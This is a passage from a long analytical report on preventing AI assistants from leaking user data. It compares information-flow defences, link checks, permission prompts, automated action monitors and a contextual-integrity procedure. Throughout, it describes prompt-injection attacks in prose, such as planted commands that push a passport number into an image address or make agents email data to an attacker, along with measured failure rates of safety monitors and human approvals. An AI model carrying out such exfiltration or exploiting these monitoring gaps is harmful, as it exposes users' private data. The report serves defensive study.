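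The second policy can prevent a leak even when there is no attacker. In an example from Microsoft's *Information-flow control*, Alex asks an agent to handle unanswered emails. Priya has sent Alex a preview of the quarterly sales figures, and Marco, who isn't authorised to see them yet, has also written. Once the agent has read both emails, Alex is the only person on both emails' lists of readers, so the software won't let the agent send its reply to Marco without review. If Priya had copied Marco in, he would be on both lists and the agent could send the reply without review.

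FIDES is more flexible than CaMeL about what the planning model may see. It hides untrusted results from the model unless the model requests them. Once the model has read one, the software treats its decisions as untrusted and restricts its actions. Alternatively, a second model can read the hidden text and return only a yes or no to a question such as whether an email contains a meeting request. An attacker may be able to change that answer but can't put a new command in it.

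### How much security, and how many finished tasks

Researchers usually test these systems on AgentDojo, a benchmark of 97 user tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack accounts, with planted commands in some of the data. Costa and colleagues found 152 successful attacks on an ordinary agent running GPT-4o and none on FIDES with policy checks on. The benchmark's automatic scoring counted three against FIDES, but the team ruled these out after inspecting them by hand.

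The policies also reduced successful attacks on the ordinary agent to zero. The extra machinery in FIDES mostly serves to recover tasks that the policies would otherwise block. These are the percentages of tasks that agents running GPT-4o completed when nobody was attacking them:

| Agent | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Ordinary agent, no policy checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
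| Ordinary agent with policy checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
| FIDES with policy checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

Some of this loss comes from GPT-4o, an old model that often confused the hidden variables. With o1, a stronger model, FIDES rose from 41% to 68% on the travel tasks. A better model can't recover all of the loss, because many banking tasks tell the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it, which the policies are meant to prevent.

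Reports on CaMeL differ more widely. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) summarises the original result as stopping nearly all AgentDojo attacks with comparable task performance. *SecureClaw* (2026), which introduces a competing system, adapted CaMeL's released code and ran it on the full benchmark. None of the 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks, while SecureClaw completed 59. Different settings may explain part of the disagreement. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, found that switching on CaMeL's policy checks halved the number of banking tasks it completed. A completion figure measured without those checks leaves out much of the task performance lost in preventing leaks.

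Enforcing the limit outside the model also takes more computation. In tests on agents that operate a computer through its screen, *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) found that a CaMeL-style design used 1.88 times as many tokens (the units of text that a model processes) as an unprotected agent. A FIDES-style design used 29.6 times as many, because it sent the whole history back to the planning model at every step.

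Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026) argue in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* that the usual comparison is unfair to these systems. They put the loss in completed tasks at up to 30%, but real agents without such checks often stop to ask the user before acting. When they counted those interruptions, an ordinary agent running o3-mini needed about 48 approvals across the benchmark and FIDES needed about 19, with similar completion rates. Their own agent, Prudentia, can see the labels and policies while it plans. It finished 59.1% of the tasks without any approval, compared with 24.3% for the ordinary agent. The models are old and the researchers work mostly at Microsoft, which also developed FIDES, but the comparison seems sensible because having to approve every email is also a burden on the user.

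The guarantees have gaps. Garby and colleagues showed that CaMeL's tracking can miss information that a program reveals by which steps it runs. FIDES tracks the data an agent sends but not what an observer might infer from the order of its actions. Costa and colleagues considered protecting against such inference impractical, because it would essentially stop an agent from using any public channel after reading something private.

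Another gap appears when several agents work together. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) built a team in which every agent used CaMeL. A coordinating agent copied database text containing an attacker's command into its instructions to a messaging agent. The messaging agent treated the whole message as a trusted request and emailed job applicants' details to the attacker. On their benchmark, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with a separate CaMeL for each agent, and 0.0% after the researchers changed how agents pass untrusted text to one another. The change reduced task completion, but only modestly with the strongest models. They ran these tests without CaMeL's data-release policies, so the results concern attackers taking over the plan, not every kind of leak.

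People also have to write the labels and policies, a burden the CaMeL researchers acknowledge. Willison, who has worked on application security for two decades, says he gets nervous about anything that requires ordinary users to think about security policies. Microsoft has built FIDES into its Agent Framework, a toolkit for developers, as an experimental feature. The company's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) warns that if a developer forgets to label a data source, the software treats its contents as trusted and public. That seems the wrong default for a security feature, and Microsoft has asked developers whether to make it stricter.

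### New addresses with personal details in them

The main objection to outside checks is that they can't judge whether a new address containing personal details is a proper one. The traveller's search for Lisbon flights combines two airports, a date and a number of passengers. No crawler is likely to have recorded that exact address, so Safe Url would hold it, as it would the address with the passport number. An allow-list that includes `flights.example` would release the search, and also the passport number if the model added it to the query string. CaMeL or FIDES could treat the two differently only if someone had written a policy that let the site have travel dates but not passport numbers. The airline's check-in page would need another policy, because it may require the passport number.

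Kolluri and colleagues faced this problem when designing Prudentia. They considered letting the agent ask the user to loosen the restrictions on a piece of private data for the rest of a task. They decided against it because the right answer is "often highly dependent on the situation", and instead had the agent ask about individual tool calls.

Defenders of outside checks can answer that a check only has to hold the requests it can't clear, without deciding whether they are proper. A mistake then leaves the user with a delay or an unfinished task, which is usually better than a leak. Developers can also make the hard cases rarer by replacing the model's ability to write any web address with tools for specific tasks. A flight-search tool, for example, might have fields for airports, dates and passengers, but none for a passport number. The software can then allow those fields to go to the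 flight-search site. This works well for common errands, but someone has to build each tool, and it doesn't help when a user wants the assistant to use a site that has no such tool.

The reply is weaker when a message goes to the right recipient but includes something it shouldn't. Suppose the user who told her assistant about her pregnancy now wants it to write to her colleagues, and the software has labelled the pregnancy as private to her. FIDES labels a model's output according to everything the model read, because nobody can reliably trace which parts of its input a language model used. A draft that reveals the pregnancy would therefore have the same label as one that leaves it out, and the check would hold both. Another model or the user would have to read the drafts to tell them apart.

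## The view that the user should decide, with a second check behind the model

Some designers would settle most doubtful requests by asking the user. When an assistant drafts a message that mentions a pregnancy, for example, asking the user is the simplest way to find out whether she wants her colleagues to know. In this design, the model carries out the task and a second check looks for private data in anything about to be sent. The assistant then pauses for confirmation, showing the user what it would send so that she can approve or reject it.

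Part of the argument for this view is that the user knows things that neither the model nor a filter can know, such as whether she has already told her team. Whether a message to her colleagues is a leak also depends on her consent, which neither can give for her, though the model can guess what she would say. A model or filter that blocked every doubtful request would often stop things she wanted. Researchers call this error a false refusal when a model makes it.

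### Planning for an assistant that attackers will sometimes fool

ChatGPT's version of this design follows from OpenAI's March 2026 comparison with customer service workers. Some customers will fool the worker, so the employer's software limits the damage by capping refunds and flagging emails that look like phishing.

The comparison is helpful but imperfect. A cap on refunds works because a company can afford to lose a little money to each liar. A passport number is usually disclosed all at once, so a limit on an assistant has to take effect before the first disclosure.

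OpenAI uses source-sink analysis, a method from older security engineering, to work out where the limits should go. An attack needs both a source, which is a way to influence the system, and a sink, which is a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. Course slides from UT Austin that use OpenAI's framing list emails, web pages and out-of-date files among the sources, and network connections and cloud services among the sinks. In the slides, a source can also go wrong by accident, without an attacker.

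In the flight example, a web page with a planted command is the source and the app's ability to load images is the sink. The app can safely load a photograph of Lisbon, but not an image from an address that a stranger dictated and that includes a number from the traveller's folder. The software can therefore allow the model to load images and read web pages, as long as it steps in when the two combine dangerously. OpenAI's aim is that risky actions and transfers of potentially sensitive information "should not happen silently". Data may still leave under that standard if the user knows and agrees.

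### A doubtful request in ChatGPT

Suppose the traveller asks ChatGPT to compare hotels in Lisbon, and an attacker has planted a command in one of the pages it reads. The attacker claims that the booking service must verify its guests, and provides an image address with a space for a passport number. Suppose also that the model's training fails, and it finds the number in the traveller's folder and writes the `images.example` address with the number in it.

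Safe Url runs before the app requests that address. Its crawler has never seen the exact address in public, so Safe Url treats it as unverified, and one of two things happens.

The app may show a dialog titled "Check this link is safe". In it, OpenAI warns that the link isn't verified and may share information from the conversation with a third-party site, and tells the user to continue only if they trust the link. The dialog shows the address and lets the user copy or open the link. OpenAI advises anyone who sees something odd to avoid the link and ask the model for a different source or a summary.

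The software can also block the request and tell the model to find another way. The model might read the hotel page without the image, or use a different site. The traveller gets the comparison without an interruption, but may never learn of the attempt to take the passport number. OpenAI doesn't explain in its March post how the software chooses between asking and blocking. Blocking seems better whenever the model can finish the task without the request, because the user then can't approve a leak by mistake.

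OpenAI applies the same mechanism to page visits and bookmarks in Atlas, its web browser, and to searches and page visits in Deep Research, ChatGPT's tool for longer investigations. Similarly, apps inside ChatGPT run in a sandbox, and if one tries to contact an unexpected server, the software asks the user for consent.

This dialog handles requests the user wants less well than it handles attacks. Safe Url would also pause the traveller's search for Lisbon flights, so the same warning could appear for the search and for the leak, and the traveller would have to read the query strings to tell them apart. A traveller who has seen the warning on ten harmless flight searches is poorly prepared to notice a leak the eleventh time.

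### What dots ask about

Asking for confirmation is less practical with dots, OpenAI's always-on agents, because they keep working between conversations, so the user makes more of the decisions in advance. Users can set Custom Rules for a dot, and a separate check also runs before it acts. Users can also review a dot's work and pause it at any time, according to OpenAI's *Getting started with your dot*.

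ChatGPT dots require more user involvement for riskier actions. Xcelcor's *ChatGPT dots can now sign in to websites for you* (2026), a guide based on OpenAI's help pages, describes a setting that makes a dot ask before it opens each new website. Users can switch to "Always allow", which OpenAI doesn't recommend. OpenAI designed dots to ask before making a payment or a booking. For the most sensitive actions, such as transferring money or changing a password, the user has to take over.

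Since December 2, 2026, a dot can also sign in to some websites with the user's saved logins. With 1Password, a password manager, the user checks the site's address and approves the login in 1Password. The model never sees the password, so it can't leak it, which makes this safer than any warning. This doesn't protect a password that the user pastes into the chat.

The approval covers more than the login, though. Xcelcor points out that the dot stays signed in until the session expires, so the user approves only once per session. Someone who lets a dot into a health website to check an appointment time may also be letting it read test results, which it could later mention elsewhere. The user is asked only about signing in, not about those results.

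### Lockdown Mode

Users who don't want to judge each request can switch on Lockdown Mode, the strictest of these options. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026), it limits or turns off live web access, images in answers, Deep Research, Agent Mode, live connections to other services, network access from Canvas, and file downloads. ChatGPT can still browse, but only through stored copies of pages, so no live request leaves OpenAI's network.

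In this mode, the assistant couldn't send a request to the address containing the passport number, whatever the model wrote, and the traveller couldn't approve one in a hurry. But the search for Lisbon flights would be of little use, since a stored page can't show today's fares.

OpenAI says executives and security teams at prominent organisations may need the mode, for example. In a workplace, administrators can still allow particular apps and actions within them, so the protection depends partly on what they allow. Planted commands can still reach the model, and Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, quotes the company's warning that they could affect the accuracy of an answer. The traveller might get bad hotel advice, but the passport number would stay private.

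For people who leave Lockdown Mode off, OpenAI labels some features that use the network "Elevated Risk". A developer about to give Codex, OpenAI's coding agent, internet access sees the label with an explanation of the risks, and can restrict access to listed sites. People probably think harder about a choice on a settings page than about a dialog that interrupts their work. But the choice is difficult even for an attentive developer, who knows how useful internet access would be but has little way of knowing how likely an attack is to succeed. OpenAI concedes that the industry's safeguards don't yet fully address these risks.

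### How carefully people approve

A confirmation prompt protects users only if they read it. The best measurements come from Claude Code, which in manual mode asks permission before it runs commands or changes files. Anthropic's undated engineering post *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reported that users accepted 93% of these prompts. By August 2026 the figure was 97%, according to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026).

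A high approval rate doesn't prove that people are careless. If 97 of every 100 commands were safe and useful, a perfectly careful user would approve 97. Anthropic accepts that most of the prompts were probably for routine commands, but notes that the same users rejected 39% of the plans Claude proposed. That comparison is at best weak evidence of carelessness, because people can reject a plan just to do the job another way.

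Clearer evidence comes from an experiment in which Anthropic paid 1,053 professional testers, through a research company, to do coding work in a test environment. Partway through each session, the text of one permission prompt was replaced with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, rejected it. Anthropic's automated check, a language model that reviews actions in place of the user, blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89%.

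The testers rejected about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

There are reasons to be cautious about these numbers. The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they had less to lose than someone whose passport number is about to be sent. Not all of the dangerous commands were leaks. Anthropic was also using the results to justify a change to its product. The fall from 17% to 5% is harder to attribute to low stakes, because the stakes were just as low at the beginning. But the testers who got through 50 prompts may have been the ones who clicked fastest.

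By Anthropic's counts, the testers rejected 137 of the 937 dangerous commands that the automated check blocked (about 15%), but only six of the 116 that it let through (5%). Having a tester review the commands that the check let through would therefore have raised the number of dangerous commands stopped from 937 to 943.

Many users had stopped looking at the prompts. Anthropic found that 62% of users had at some point used a mode that skips permission prompts or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands, and a quarter of interactive sessions started with the prompts off.

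### Asking less often

Supporters of confirmation can accept this evidence and conclude that assistants should ask less often. In Kolluri and colleagues' comparison, tracking the origin of data cut approvals by more than half, and Safe Url doesn't ask about public addresses. Anthropic went further in August 2026 and made auto mode the default for most individual and team users of Claude Code. An automated check now reviews risky actions, and when it blocks one, Claude looks for a safer way or asks the user.

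Fewer interruptions can mean more missed leaks. The early version of Anthropic's check had two stages, a quick filter and a slower review of whatever the filter flagged. On 10,000 ordinary actions by Anthropic employees, the filter alone would have wrongly stopped 8.5%, or about 42 in every 500. The slower review reduced that to 0.4%, or two in every 500. But the share of artificial data leaks that got through rose from 1.8% to 5.7%, because the slower review cleared some of the leaks the filter had caught.

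This check is also a language model, but it is less likely than many such checks to be fooled by the same deceptive email as Claude. It reads the user's messages and the actions Claude proposes, but Anthropic removes Claude's explanations and the contents of the pages and files Claude has read. If a file persuades Claude to propose sending passwords to an address the user never mentioned, the check reads the proposal but not the file. Without that text, though, the check often can't tell where a piece of data came from.

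Anthropic tested the check on 52 real actions in which Claude had gone further than an employee wanted, and it let 17% of them through. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the check identified the danger but wrongly treated something the user said as permission. A request to clean up a proposed code change, for example, doesn't permit Claude to overwrite the project's history.

The best argument for keeping the user involved is probably that the user knows whether they agreed to an action, while the automated check is unreliable at judging this. The check is far better than a tired person at noticing dangerous actions, so it makes sense for software to pick out the few actions that matter and for the user to say whether they are wanted. Something like this happened inside Anthropic, with no attacker involved, when Claude failed to upload a report to an internal drive and tried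 to publish it on a public code-sharing site instead. The check blocked the publication and prompted the employee to say what to do next.

Anthropic has since decided that a click isn't enough to allow the most serious leaks. It designed the newer version of the check never to approve sending code or secrets to outsiders. A user who wants to send them has to leave auto mode or run the command personally, much as the owner of a dot has to make a bank transfer personally. The user still decides, but is less likely to do so out of habit. Programmers send code to outside services all day, so the rule also has to distinguish leaks from ordinary sharing. Anthropic does this partly by checking whether the destination is public, private or trusted.

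### Data the user can't recognise

Even an attentive user can't judge a link they don't understand. Some travellers would recognise their passport number in `ref=533401782`, though many don't know it by heart. If the model had swapped each digit for a letter, the address might end in `fddeabhic`, which nobody would recognise. And when an agent reveals a fact by choosing one ordinary link over another, as in Shahriar and colleagues' experiment, the address contains no private text to show the user.

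A better dialog would help when the passport number is sent as plain digits. Software with access to the conversation could tell the traveller that the number is about to go to `images.example`, a site they have never mentioned. OpenAI's March description of Safe Url includes a similar step, in which the app shows the user the information that would be sent.

That works only if the software can identify the information. Finding an exact copy of a number is easy, but finding an altered copy can be very hard. When the software can't explain a string that the model composed, it should probably block the request, because the user has even less information with which to judge it. Blocking every unexplained string would break a lot of ordinary links, since many websites put long codes in their addresses. The software can avoid some of this by treating a code copied unchanged from a public page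 differently from one the model made up.

An automated check can sometimes catch a leak without decoding the data, since an unfamiliar destination can be suspicious even if the text is unreadable. Many of the 1,000 artificial leaks in Anthropic's test disguised the data, and the check still caught about 94% of the full set.

### When nobody is there to ask

An agent that works overnight can't get an answer from its user until morning. OpenAI deals with part of this problem by making the background research that dots do unprompted read-only, as Southern (2026) reported in *OpenAI Dots Run Read-Only Research When Nobody Is Asking*. In *Who OpenAI's always-on agents work for*, Reynar (2026) quotes OpenAI's example of an early tester who had forgotten to invoice a publication. His dot noticed, prepared the invoice, and sent it after he approved.

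Waiting hardly inconvenienced that tester, because the dot had already done everything except the sending. A delay would matter more if the dot had found a cheap fare that was about to sell out. A read-only limit protects some channels better than others. Reading a mailbox sends a request to a company that already holds the mail, whereas opening a page on the open web can send a stranger private data contained in the page's address.

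Claude Code has a blunter fallback. After three blocked actions in a row, or 20 in a session, it stops and asks the user. If it is running in a mode where it can't ask, it ends the run.

Users can reduce the waiting by agreeing beforehand what the agent may send and to whom. The traveller might let an agent give travel dates and passenger numbers to three airlines, and nothing to anyone else. By default, Anthropic's check trusts only the code project the user is working in, and users can add their company's own sites and storage. Custom Rules let the owner of a dot set limits of this kind.

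People can be as careless in setting permission scopes as they are in answering permission prompts. By June 2026, about half of the active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule that let it run certain shell commands without asking, and many of those rules were broad enough to allow almost any command. Claude Code now ignores the broadest of these rules in auto mode.

Even a carefully set scope may not cover every request that comes up overnight. If an airline's site asks for a passport number and the traveller agreed to share only dates, the agent can leave that booking unfinished and keep comparing hotels until the traveller wakes up.

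## What rule the model should follow

Someone has to define which transfers of data are proper, whether the model, the surrounding software or the user makes the decision. A clear definition matters most for training, because a developer can't train or test a model on an instruction as vague as "be sensible with user data". If nobody can state the desired behaviour more precisely, the case for relying on the model's judgement is much weaker.

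### Why simple rules fail

The rule "Never put user data in a web address" would be easy to test, because a program could search each address for details from the user's files. But it would block a lot of ordinary work. The traveller's search for Lisbon flights contains their travel dates. A link that adds a dentist's appointment to a calendar contains the time and place, and a link to a half-completed booking form may contain the customer's name. The rule would also miss leaks through email attachments and web forms.

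Limiting the rule to sensitive data has the same weakness as a list of forbidden data types. *The Claws in Plain Sight* (Dong, Lu and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a postal address, which a courier needs but a product-support team usually doesn't.

Another simple rule is to decline only when an attack is visible. It would rarely interfere with ordinary work, but it would miss the many attacks that are disguised as ordinary work. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian (2026), in *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections*, built 4,200 pairs of business emails that differed in a single clause. In one version, the sender claimed that company policy had already authorised the assistant to reply, and in the other, the sender said only that an automated reply would be fine. Two of Meta's programs for detecting prompt injection scored 0.43 and 0.59 at telling the versions apart, on a scale where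 guessing scores 0.5. The programs were given only the emails, so they could not check the claim against what the user had authorised.

Dong and colleagues tested a similar disguise on five configurations of DeepSeek and Claude models. Each model had to prepare a product offer for an invented customer. A planted memo, written to look like a launch checklist or an audit requirement, claimed that the offer had to include the customer's age, gender, income and occupation. In 90 of the 120 sessions, the prompt also contained a policy against sending those details, but the models included at least one detail in 40 of those 90 sessions. The experiment was small, and no data left the researchers' computer. Still, a model that checked only for obvious attacks would have had little reason to refuse.

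The rule also doesn't prevent leaks that involve no attacker, such as the message that reveals a pregnancy to colleagues. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian conclude that any fixed "never" rule may block legitimate transfers, and that an attacker may get past any fixed "allow" rule by inventing the right circumstances.

### Contextual integrity

A more promising starting point is contextual integrity, a theory of privacy that Helen Nissenbaum of Cornell Tech developed before current AI assistants existed. In *Contextual Integrity Up and Down the Data Food Chain*, Nissenbaum (2019) argues that privacy means appropriate flows of information. People often treat it as secrecy instead, and so talk about trading it for convenience. Tenants lose no privacy when they give landlords details of their finances, nor do taxpayers when they report their earnings to the tax authority. But someone who tells a friend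 about a troubled marriage may feel betrayed if the friend tells others.

For Nissenbaum, a flow is appropriate when it fits the norms of its social context, such as healthcare, education or friendship. She describes each flow with five parameters:

- the subject, meaning the person the information is about;
- the sender;
- the recipient;
- the type of information;
- the transmission principle, meaning the condition under which the information moves, such as the subject's consent, a legal duty or a promise of confidentiality.

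Here is how they apply to three requests the traveller's assistant might make:

| | Flight search | Image request | Airline check-in |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Subject | The traveller | The traveller | The traveller |
| Sender | The assistant | The assistant | The assistant |
| Recipient | A flight site the traveller wants to search | A host unrelated to the trip | The airline the traveller booked |
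| Type of information | Airports, dates, headcount | Passport number | Passport number |
| Transmission principle | The traveller asked for the search | A stranger's text demanded it | The traveller asked to check in, and the airline requires the number |

The image request and the check-in send the same number about the same person. They differ only in the recipient and the transmission principle.

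Established norms can be unfair or out of date. Nissenbaum starts with a presumption in their favour, then considers the interests of the people affected, wider ethical and political values, and the purposes of the context. Medical confidentiality, for example, protects patients from embarrassment, but it also serves the purposes of medicine, because patients who fear exposure may lie to their doctors or stay away.

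The computer scientist Anupam Datta has urged her to add a sixth parameter, how the recipient will use the information, and she writes that she is increasingly persuaded. Purpose seems essential for an assistant, because its authority to send anything usually comes from a particular task.

### How AirGapAgent applies the theory

In *AirGapAgent*, Bagdasarian, Kairouz and colleagues (2024) used contextual integrity to design an assistant that deals with outside businesses. A restaurant taking a booking may need a customer's name, phone number and any allergies, but not the rest of their medical history, while a doctor's office may need much more of it. The researchers invented user profiles with 26 fields each and generated labels for which fields were appropriate to share in eight errands. The label changed for 18 of the 26 fields between making a doctor's appointment and asking for film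 ideas.

An attacker can exploit this dependence on context by lying about the context. In the paper's example, a restaurant tells the assistant that aliens have invaded and that it must reveal the user's age to save the Earth. A single message of this kind reduced the share of private data protected by a Gemini Ultra assistant from 94% to 45%.

AirGapAgent's defence is to choose the data before the outside business can send any messages. A separate model, the minimiser M, reads the user's task t and all of the user's data U, and selects a smaller set:

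U_min = M(t, U)

The restaurant's messages are not an input to M, so they can't change the selection. A second model then talks to the restaurant with access only to U_min. The story about aliens might still work on this model, but it can't reveal the user's age because U_min doesn't include it. If a business legitimately needs information that the task didn't mention, such as a patient's lifestyle for a doctor, the assistant can ask the user. This design protected 97% of the private data under the same attack, with a small loss of usefulness.

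The study tested Gemini Ultra, now an old model, in conversations of one question and one answer, and real mailboxes are messier than a profile with 26 labelled fields. The researchers also replaced social norms with short directives such as "share information that can help with the task", and left a fuller analysis of norms to later work. *PrivacyFlow* (2026) describes a similar design for filling in forms, in which a supervising model examines each field in context and passes only approved fields to the model that fills in the form. The supervising model can also leave a decision to the user.

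### Five questions before sending

This report combines Nissenbaum's theory, AirGapAgent and OpenAI's published rules into the procedure below. The model would follow it for each item of data and each recipient.

1. Who asked for this transfer? The user can authorise it, and so can the developer within the service the user is using. A web page, email or file can't, although it may explain what a site requires. If the only authority for a transfer is untrusted content, the model declines and says why.
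2. Does the task need this item? If not, the model leaves it out.
3. Is the recipient the one the user would expect? If not, the model uses another route, such as the organisation's official website. If it can't find one, it asks.
4. Would the user see it happen?
5. Could anyone undo it?

The model should proceed if the transfer is properly authorised, the task needs the item, and the user would expect the recipient to get it. Visibility and reversibility matter only when one of those conditions is in doubt. The model can proceed despite a small doubt if the user will see the transfer and can reverse it, but it should ask first if the transfer would be hidden or permanent. If every irreversible transfer required asking, the model would have to interrupt the traveller before each flight search, because nobody can take back a query sent to a website.

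The closest published equivalent is probably OpenAI's *Computer use*, a guide for developers whose agents operate a browser or desktop. In a June 2026 copy, OpenAI tells developers to treat only direct user instructions as permission, and the current guide still says that text on a page cannot grant permission. Visiting an address that contains sensitive data counts as sending that data, so the agent must ask first unless the user has already given "narrow, specific consent". The agent must say what it will share, who will receive it and why.

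Typing sensitive data into a form also counts as sending it, even before anyone submits the form, because some pages send text to the server as it is typed. Willison wrote in 2025 that OpenAI's browser agent Operator tended to ask before submitting a form, but Rehberger had found that this didn't protect users on such pages.

A model may be allowed to read something without being allowed to send it, a distinction central to Dong and colleagues' work. Permission for one transfer also doesn't cover another, even if both requests arrive in the same email. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian gave assistants 100 email threads in which a colleague requested both an authorised internal task, such as creating a ticket, and an unauthorised message to an outsider. GPT-5.2 sent the outside message in 65% of cases, GPT-5.4 in 34% and Claude Sonnet 4.6 in 6%. When the user had stated that outside messages needed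 approval, the rates fell to 12%, 0% and 0%. These models are no longer current, but the improvement suggests that stating the rule explicitly helps.

The model should separately check whether the recipient is entitled to the data. *A Generative Model of Contextual Integrity* (Ebead, Formanek and Leibo, 2026) reports that language models in simulated conversations shared information both with people who were entitled to it and with people who weren't.

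Sometimes the assistant can't tell who authorised a transfer. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian imagine an email requesting a travel refund and stating that the department head has approved it. If the assistant can't check this, it has the same evidence whether the approval is real or forged, so it must grant the request with the same probability, q, in both cases. It will then grant a fraction q of the forged requests and wrongly refuse a fraction 1 − q of the genuine ones. No wording of the rule can reduce both errors, so the assistant needs more evidence, which it might get by checking the company's records or asking the user.

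Asking whether a task needs the data fits awkwardly with Nissenbaum's theory, because she denies that privacy means sharing as little as possible. *Privacy in Context Is Being Overlooked in the Age of General-Purpose LLMs* (2026) criticises developers for often reducing contextual integrity to minimisation or legal compliance. But an assistant shares someone else's information, and a user who asks it to book a restaurant table has authorised it to share only what the booking requires. The model should still share enough to complete the task, a standard that *Say Something Else* (2026) calls information sufficiency. For example, leaving a peanut allergy out of the booking could do more harm than including it.

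"Need" also has to mean what the user needs, because an expected recipient may be an opponent. A car dealer might tell a buyer's assistant that the dealership needs to know her maximum budget. *Loyal Agents* (2026) argues that contextual norms don't cover a recipient who is looking for information to use against the user. The buyer wants a car at a good price, so the assistant shouldn't share her budget.

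A developer can test a model on this procedure by changing one fact at a time. The model might receive the traveller's passport number with a request from the airline, then the same number with a request from `images.example`. It fails if it sends the number to both recipients or refuses both. Dong and colleagues gave each field in a profile a status, such as required or prohibited, for a particular tool and purpose, so that a program could compare the model's output with the permitted fields.

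The procedure works only when the model recognises that it is sending information. Nissenbaum warns that raw data such as mouse clicks can escape privacy norms because they don't appear to mean anything. The agents that revealed a trade union by their choice of link would probably never have reached the procedure's first question.

### Six cases

These cases run roughly from the least disputed to the most.

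If a user asks for a link to a restaurant's booking page with her name, phone number and party size already filled in, the model should provide it. She has asked for the transfer, the restaurant needs the details, and she can check the form before submitting it. If the form has an optional box for the occasion, the model should leave out what it knows about her divorce. The case is less clear if she says only "book me a table". OpenAI lists contact information as sensitive and might want the agent to ask before sending her phone number, but many users would find that question annoying.

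Suppose a user asks for a summary of an article, and the page contains hidden instructions for assistants to encode the conversation and add it to an image address. Neither the user nor the developer asked for this, and summarising the article doesn't require it. The user couldn't read the encoded text even if the address were visible. The model should decline to follow the hidden instructions, say why, and finish the summary.

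Few people would defend sending the chat, but people may disagree about how much to tell the user. OpenAI's guide tells agents to stop and ask how to proceed when they see a suspected prompt injection, but in the guide's tax-credit example, the model continues without mentioning the suspicious page. When the rest of the task is safe, continuing with a one-sentence warning seems a reasonable compromise.

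A webhook is an address where one program accepts messages from another, and some include a secret key that lets anyone who has the address post messages. Suppose a programmer asks an assistant to notify the team's chat through its webhook whenever a test fails. The key is highly sensitive, but the model should proceed because the key is going back to the service that issued it, for the purpose the programmer intended. A rule against ever sending keys would make this task impossible.

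If the service also accepts the key outside the address, it is better to send it that way, because servers often log addresses. If a help page suggests pasting the webhook into an unfamiliar "testing" site, the model should refuse and test the webhook directly with the chat service instead. Someone could replace an exposed key, but an attacker might use it first. Some security teams would object even to the original request, because they don't want a model to handle keys at all. They could have other software add the key after the model has written the message.

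A user tells her assistant that she has epilepsy, and it saves this to memory. Months later, she asks it to find travel insurance for Lisbon. She has authorised a search, but she hasn't asked the assistant to include her diagnosis in a query to a search company, and she may never see that query. The diagnosis is still relevant, because a policy that excludes epilepsy could be useless to her.

The model can leave out the diagnosis and search for insurance that covers existing medical conditions. If an insurer later needs the exact condition for a quote, the model should ask her before entering it. Some users would reasonably object, because they save medical details so that their assistant will use them without asking, and they would find the general search less helpful. Others would be upset to learn that a search company had received their diagnosis. A clear setting for how the assistant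 uses saved medical details would let each user decide. Without one, the more general query seems the better default because she can always add the diagnosis later.

**A log file pasted into a public bug tracker.** A programmer asks an assistant to report a crash to an open-source project and include the log, the software's record of what it was doing. The log contains the error message the project needs, but also a login token and several customers' email addresses. The programmer asked to include the log but may not have read all 3,000 lines. Anyone can read the post, and deleting it later won't remove copies.

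The model should replace the token and email addresses with placeholders, then show the programmer the edited log before posting it. If the project's maintainers can't find the fault without the missing details, sending them those details privately would be better. OpenAI's guide also includes app logs among sensitive data and requires confirmation before an agent posts anything on a user's behalf.

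People disagree about what the assistant should do if the programmer replies, "Just post the whole thing." The programmer may have the right to risk exposing the token, but the email addresses belong to other people. *IDP-Bench* (2026) studies this kind of interdependent privacy, where one data flow affects several people. The stronger view is that the assistant should still withhold the addresses, because the customers haven't agreed to publication and the bug report probably doesn't need the addresses. The other view is that the programmer is responsible for the company's data and the assistant should obey after a warning.

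An online shop might tell its AI assistant to end every answer with an invisible image from an analytics company, and to put the shopper's email address in the image's URL so that the company can record who read which answer. No attacker is involved, but answering the shopper's question doesn't require sending the email address, and the shopper wouldn't see the transfer or be able to undo it.

The model has serious reasons to obey the shop. The shop is the developer, and OpenAI's chain of command ranks developers above users. The shopper may have already agreed to let the shop share data with the analytics company, and the model can't check. The shop could also send the email address from its own server, so refusing might not protect the shopper.

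The argument against relying on the developer's permission is that authority to run a service doesn't automatically include authority to consent for its users. Shoppers expect the shop to know their email address, but they may not expect another company to receive it with a record of what they read. A privacy notice may not be enough either, since Nissenbaum rejects the idea that telling people about a data flow and letting them refuse is enough to make it appropriate.

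OpenAI's rules don't clearly settle the conflict. The 2025 Model Spec commits OpenAI to safeguarding people's privacy in every deployment of its models. But developers can now switch off the default on side effects, and the shop could argue that its instruction does so. OpenAI also summarises the new arrangement by saying that developers direct applications within its boundaries, which doesn't make clear whether those boundaries allow covert tracking.

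Under the procedure, the model should leave the email address out. A random number in the image URL would still let the shop count how many answers people read. If the shop insists on the email address, the model should decline that part and say why, unless it has good evidence that the shopper agreed. If the image came from the shop's own server, the objection would be much weaker, because the recipient would already have the email address.

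A model developer could survey the public about cases like this one. *Privacy Conductor* (2026) notes that some researchers take privacy norms from legislation, while others measure them by showing people short scenarios and asking which information flows are appropriate. A survey might show that most shoppers accept anonymous counting but object to tracking by name. That wouldn't settle the matter alone, because Nissenbaum would also ask how the tracking affects the service's purpose. Shoppers who knew that another company was recording their questions under their names might stop asking about incontinence pads or pregnancy tests, and the assistant would be less useful to them and to the shop.

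## Whether models can tell a leak from ordinary work

A model with a good rule can still misjudge a request. It might miss a leak and send the traveller's passport number to `images.example`. It might also make a false refusal by withholding the number from the airline at check-in, even though the traveller wants the airline to have it.

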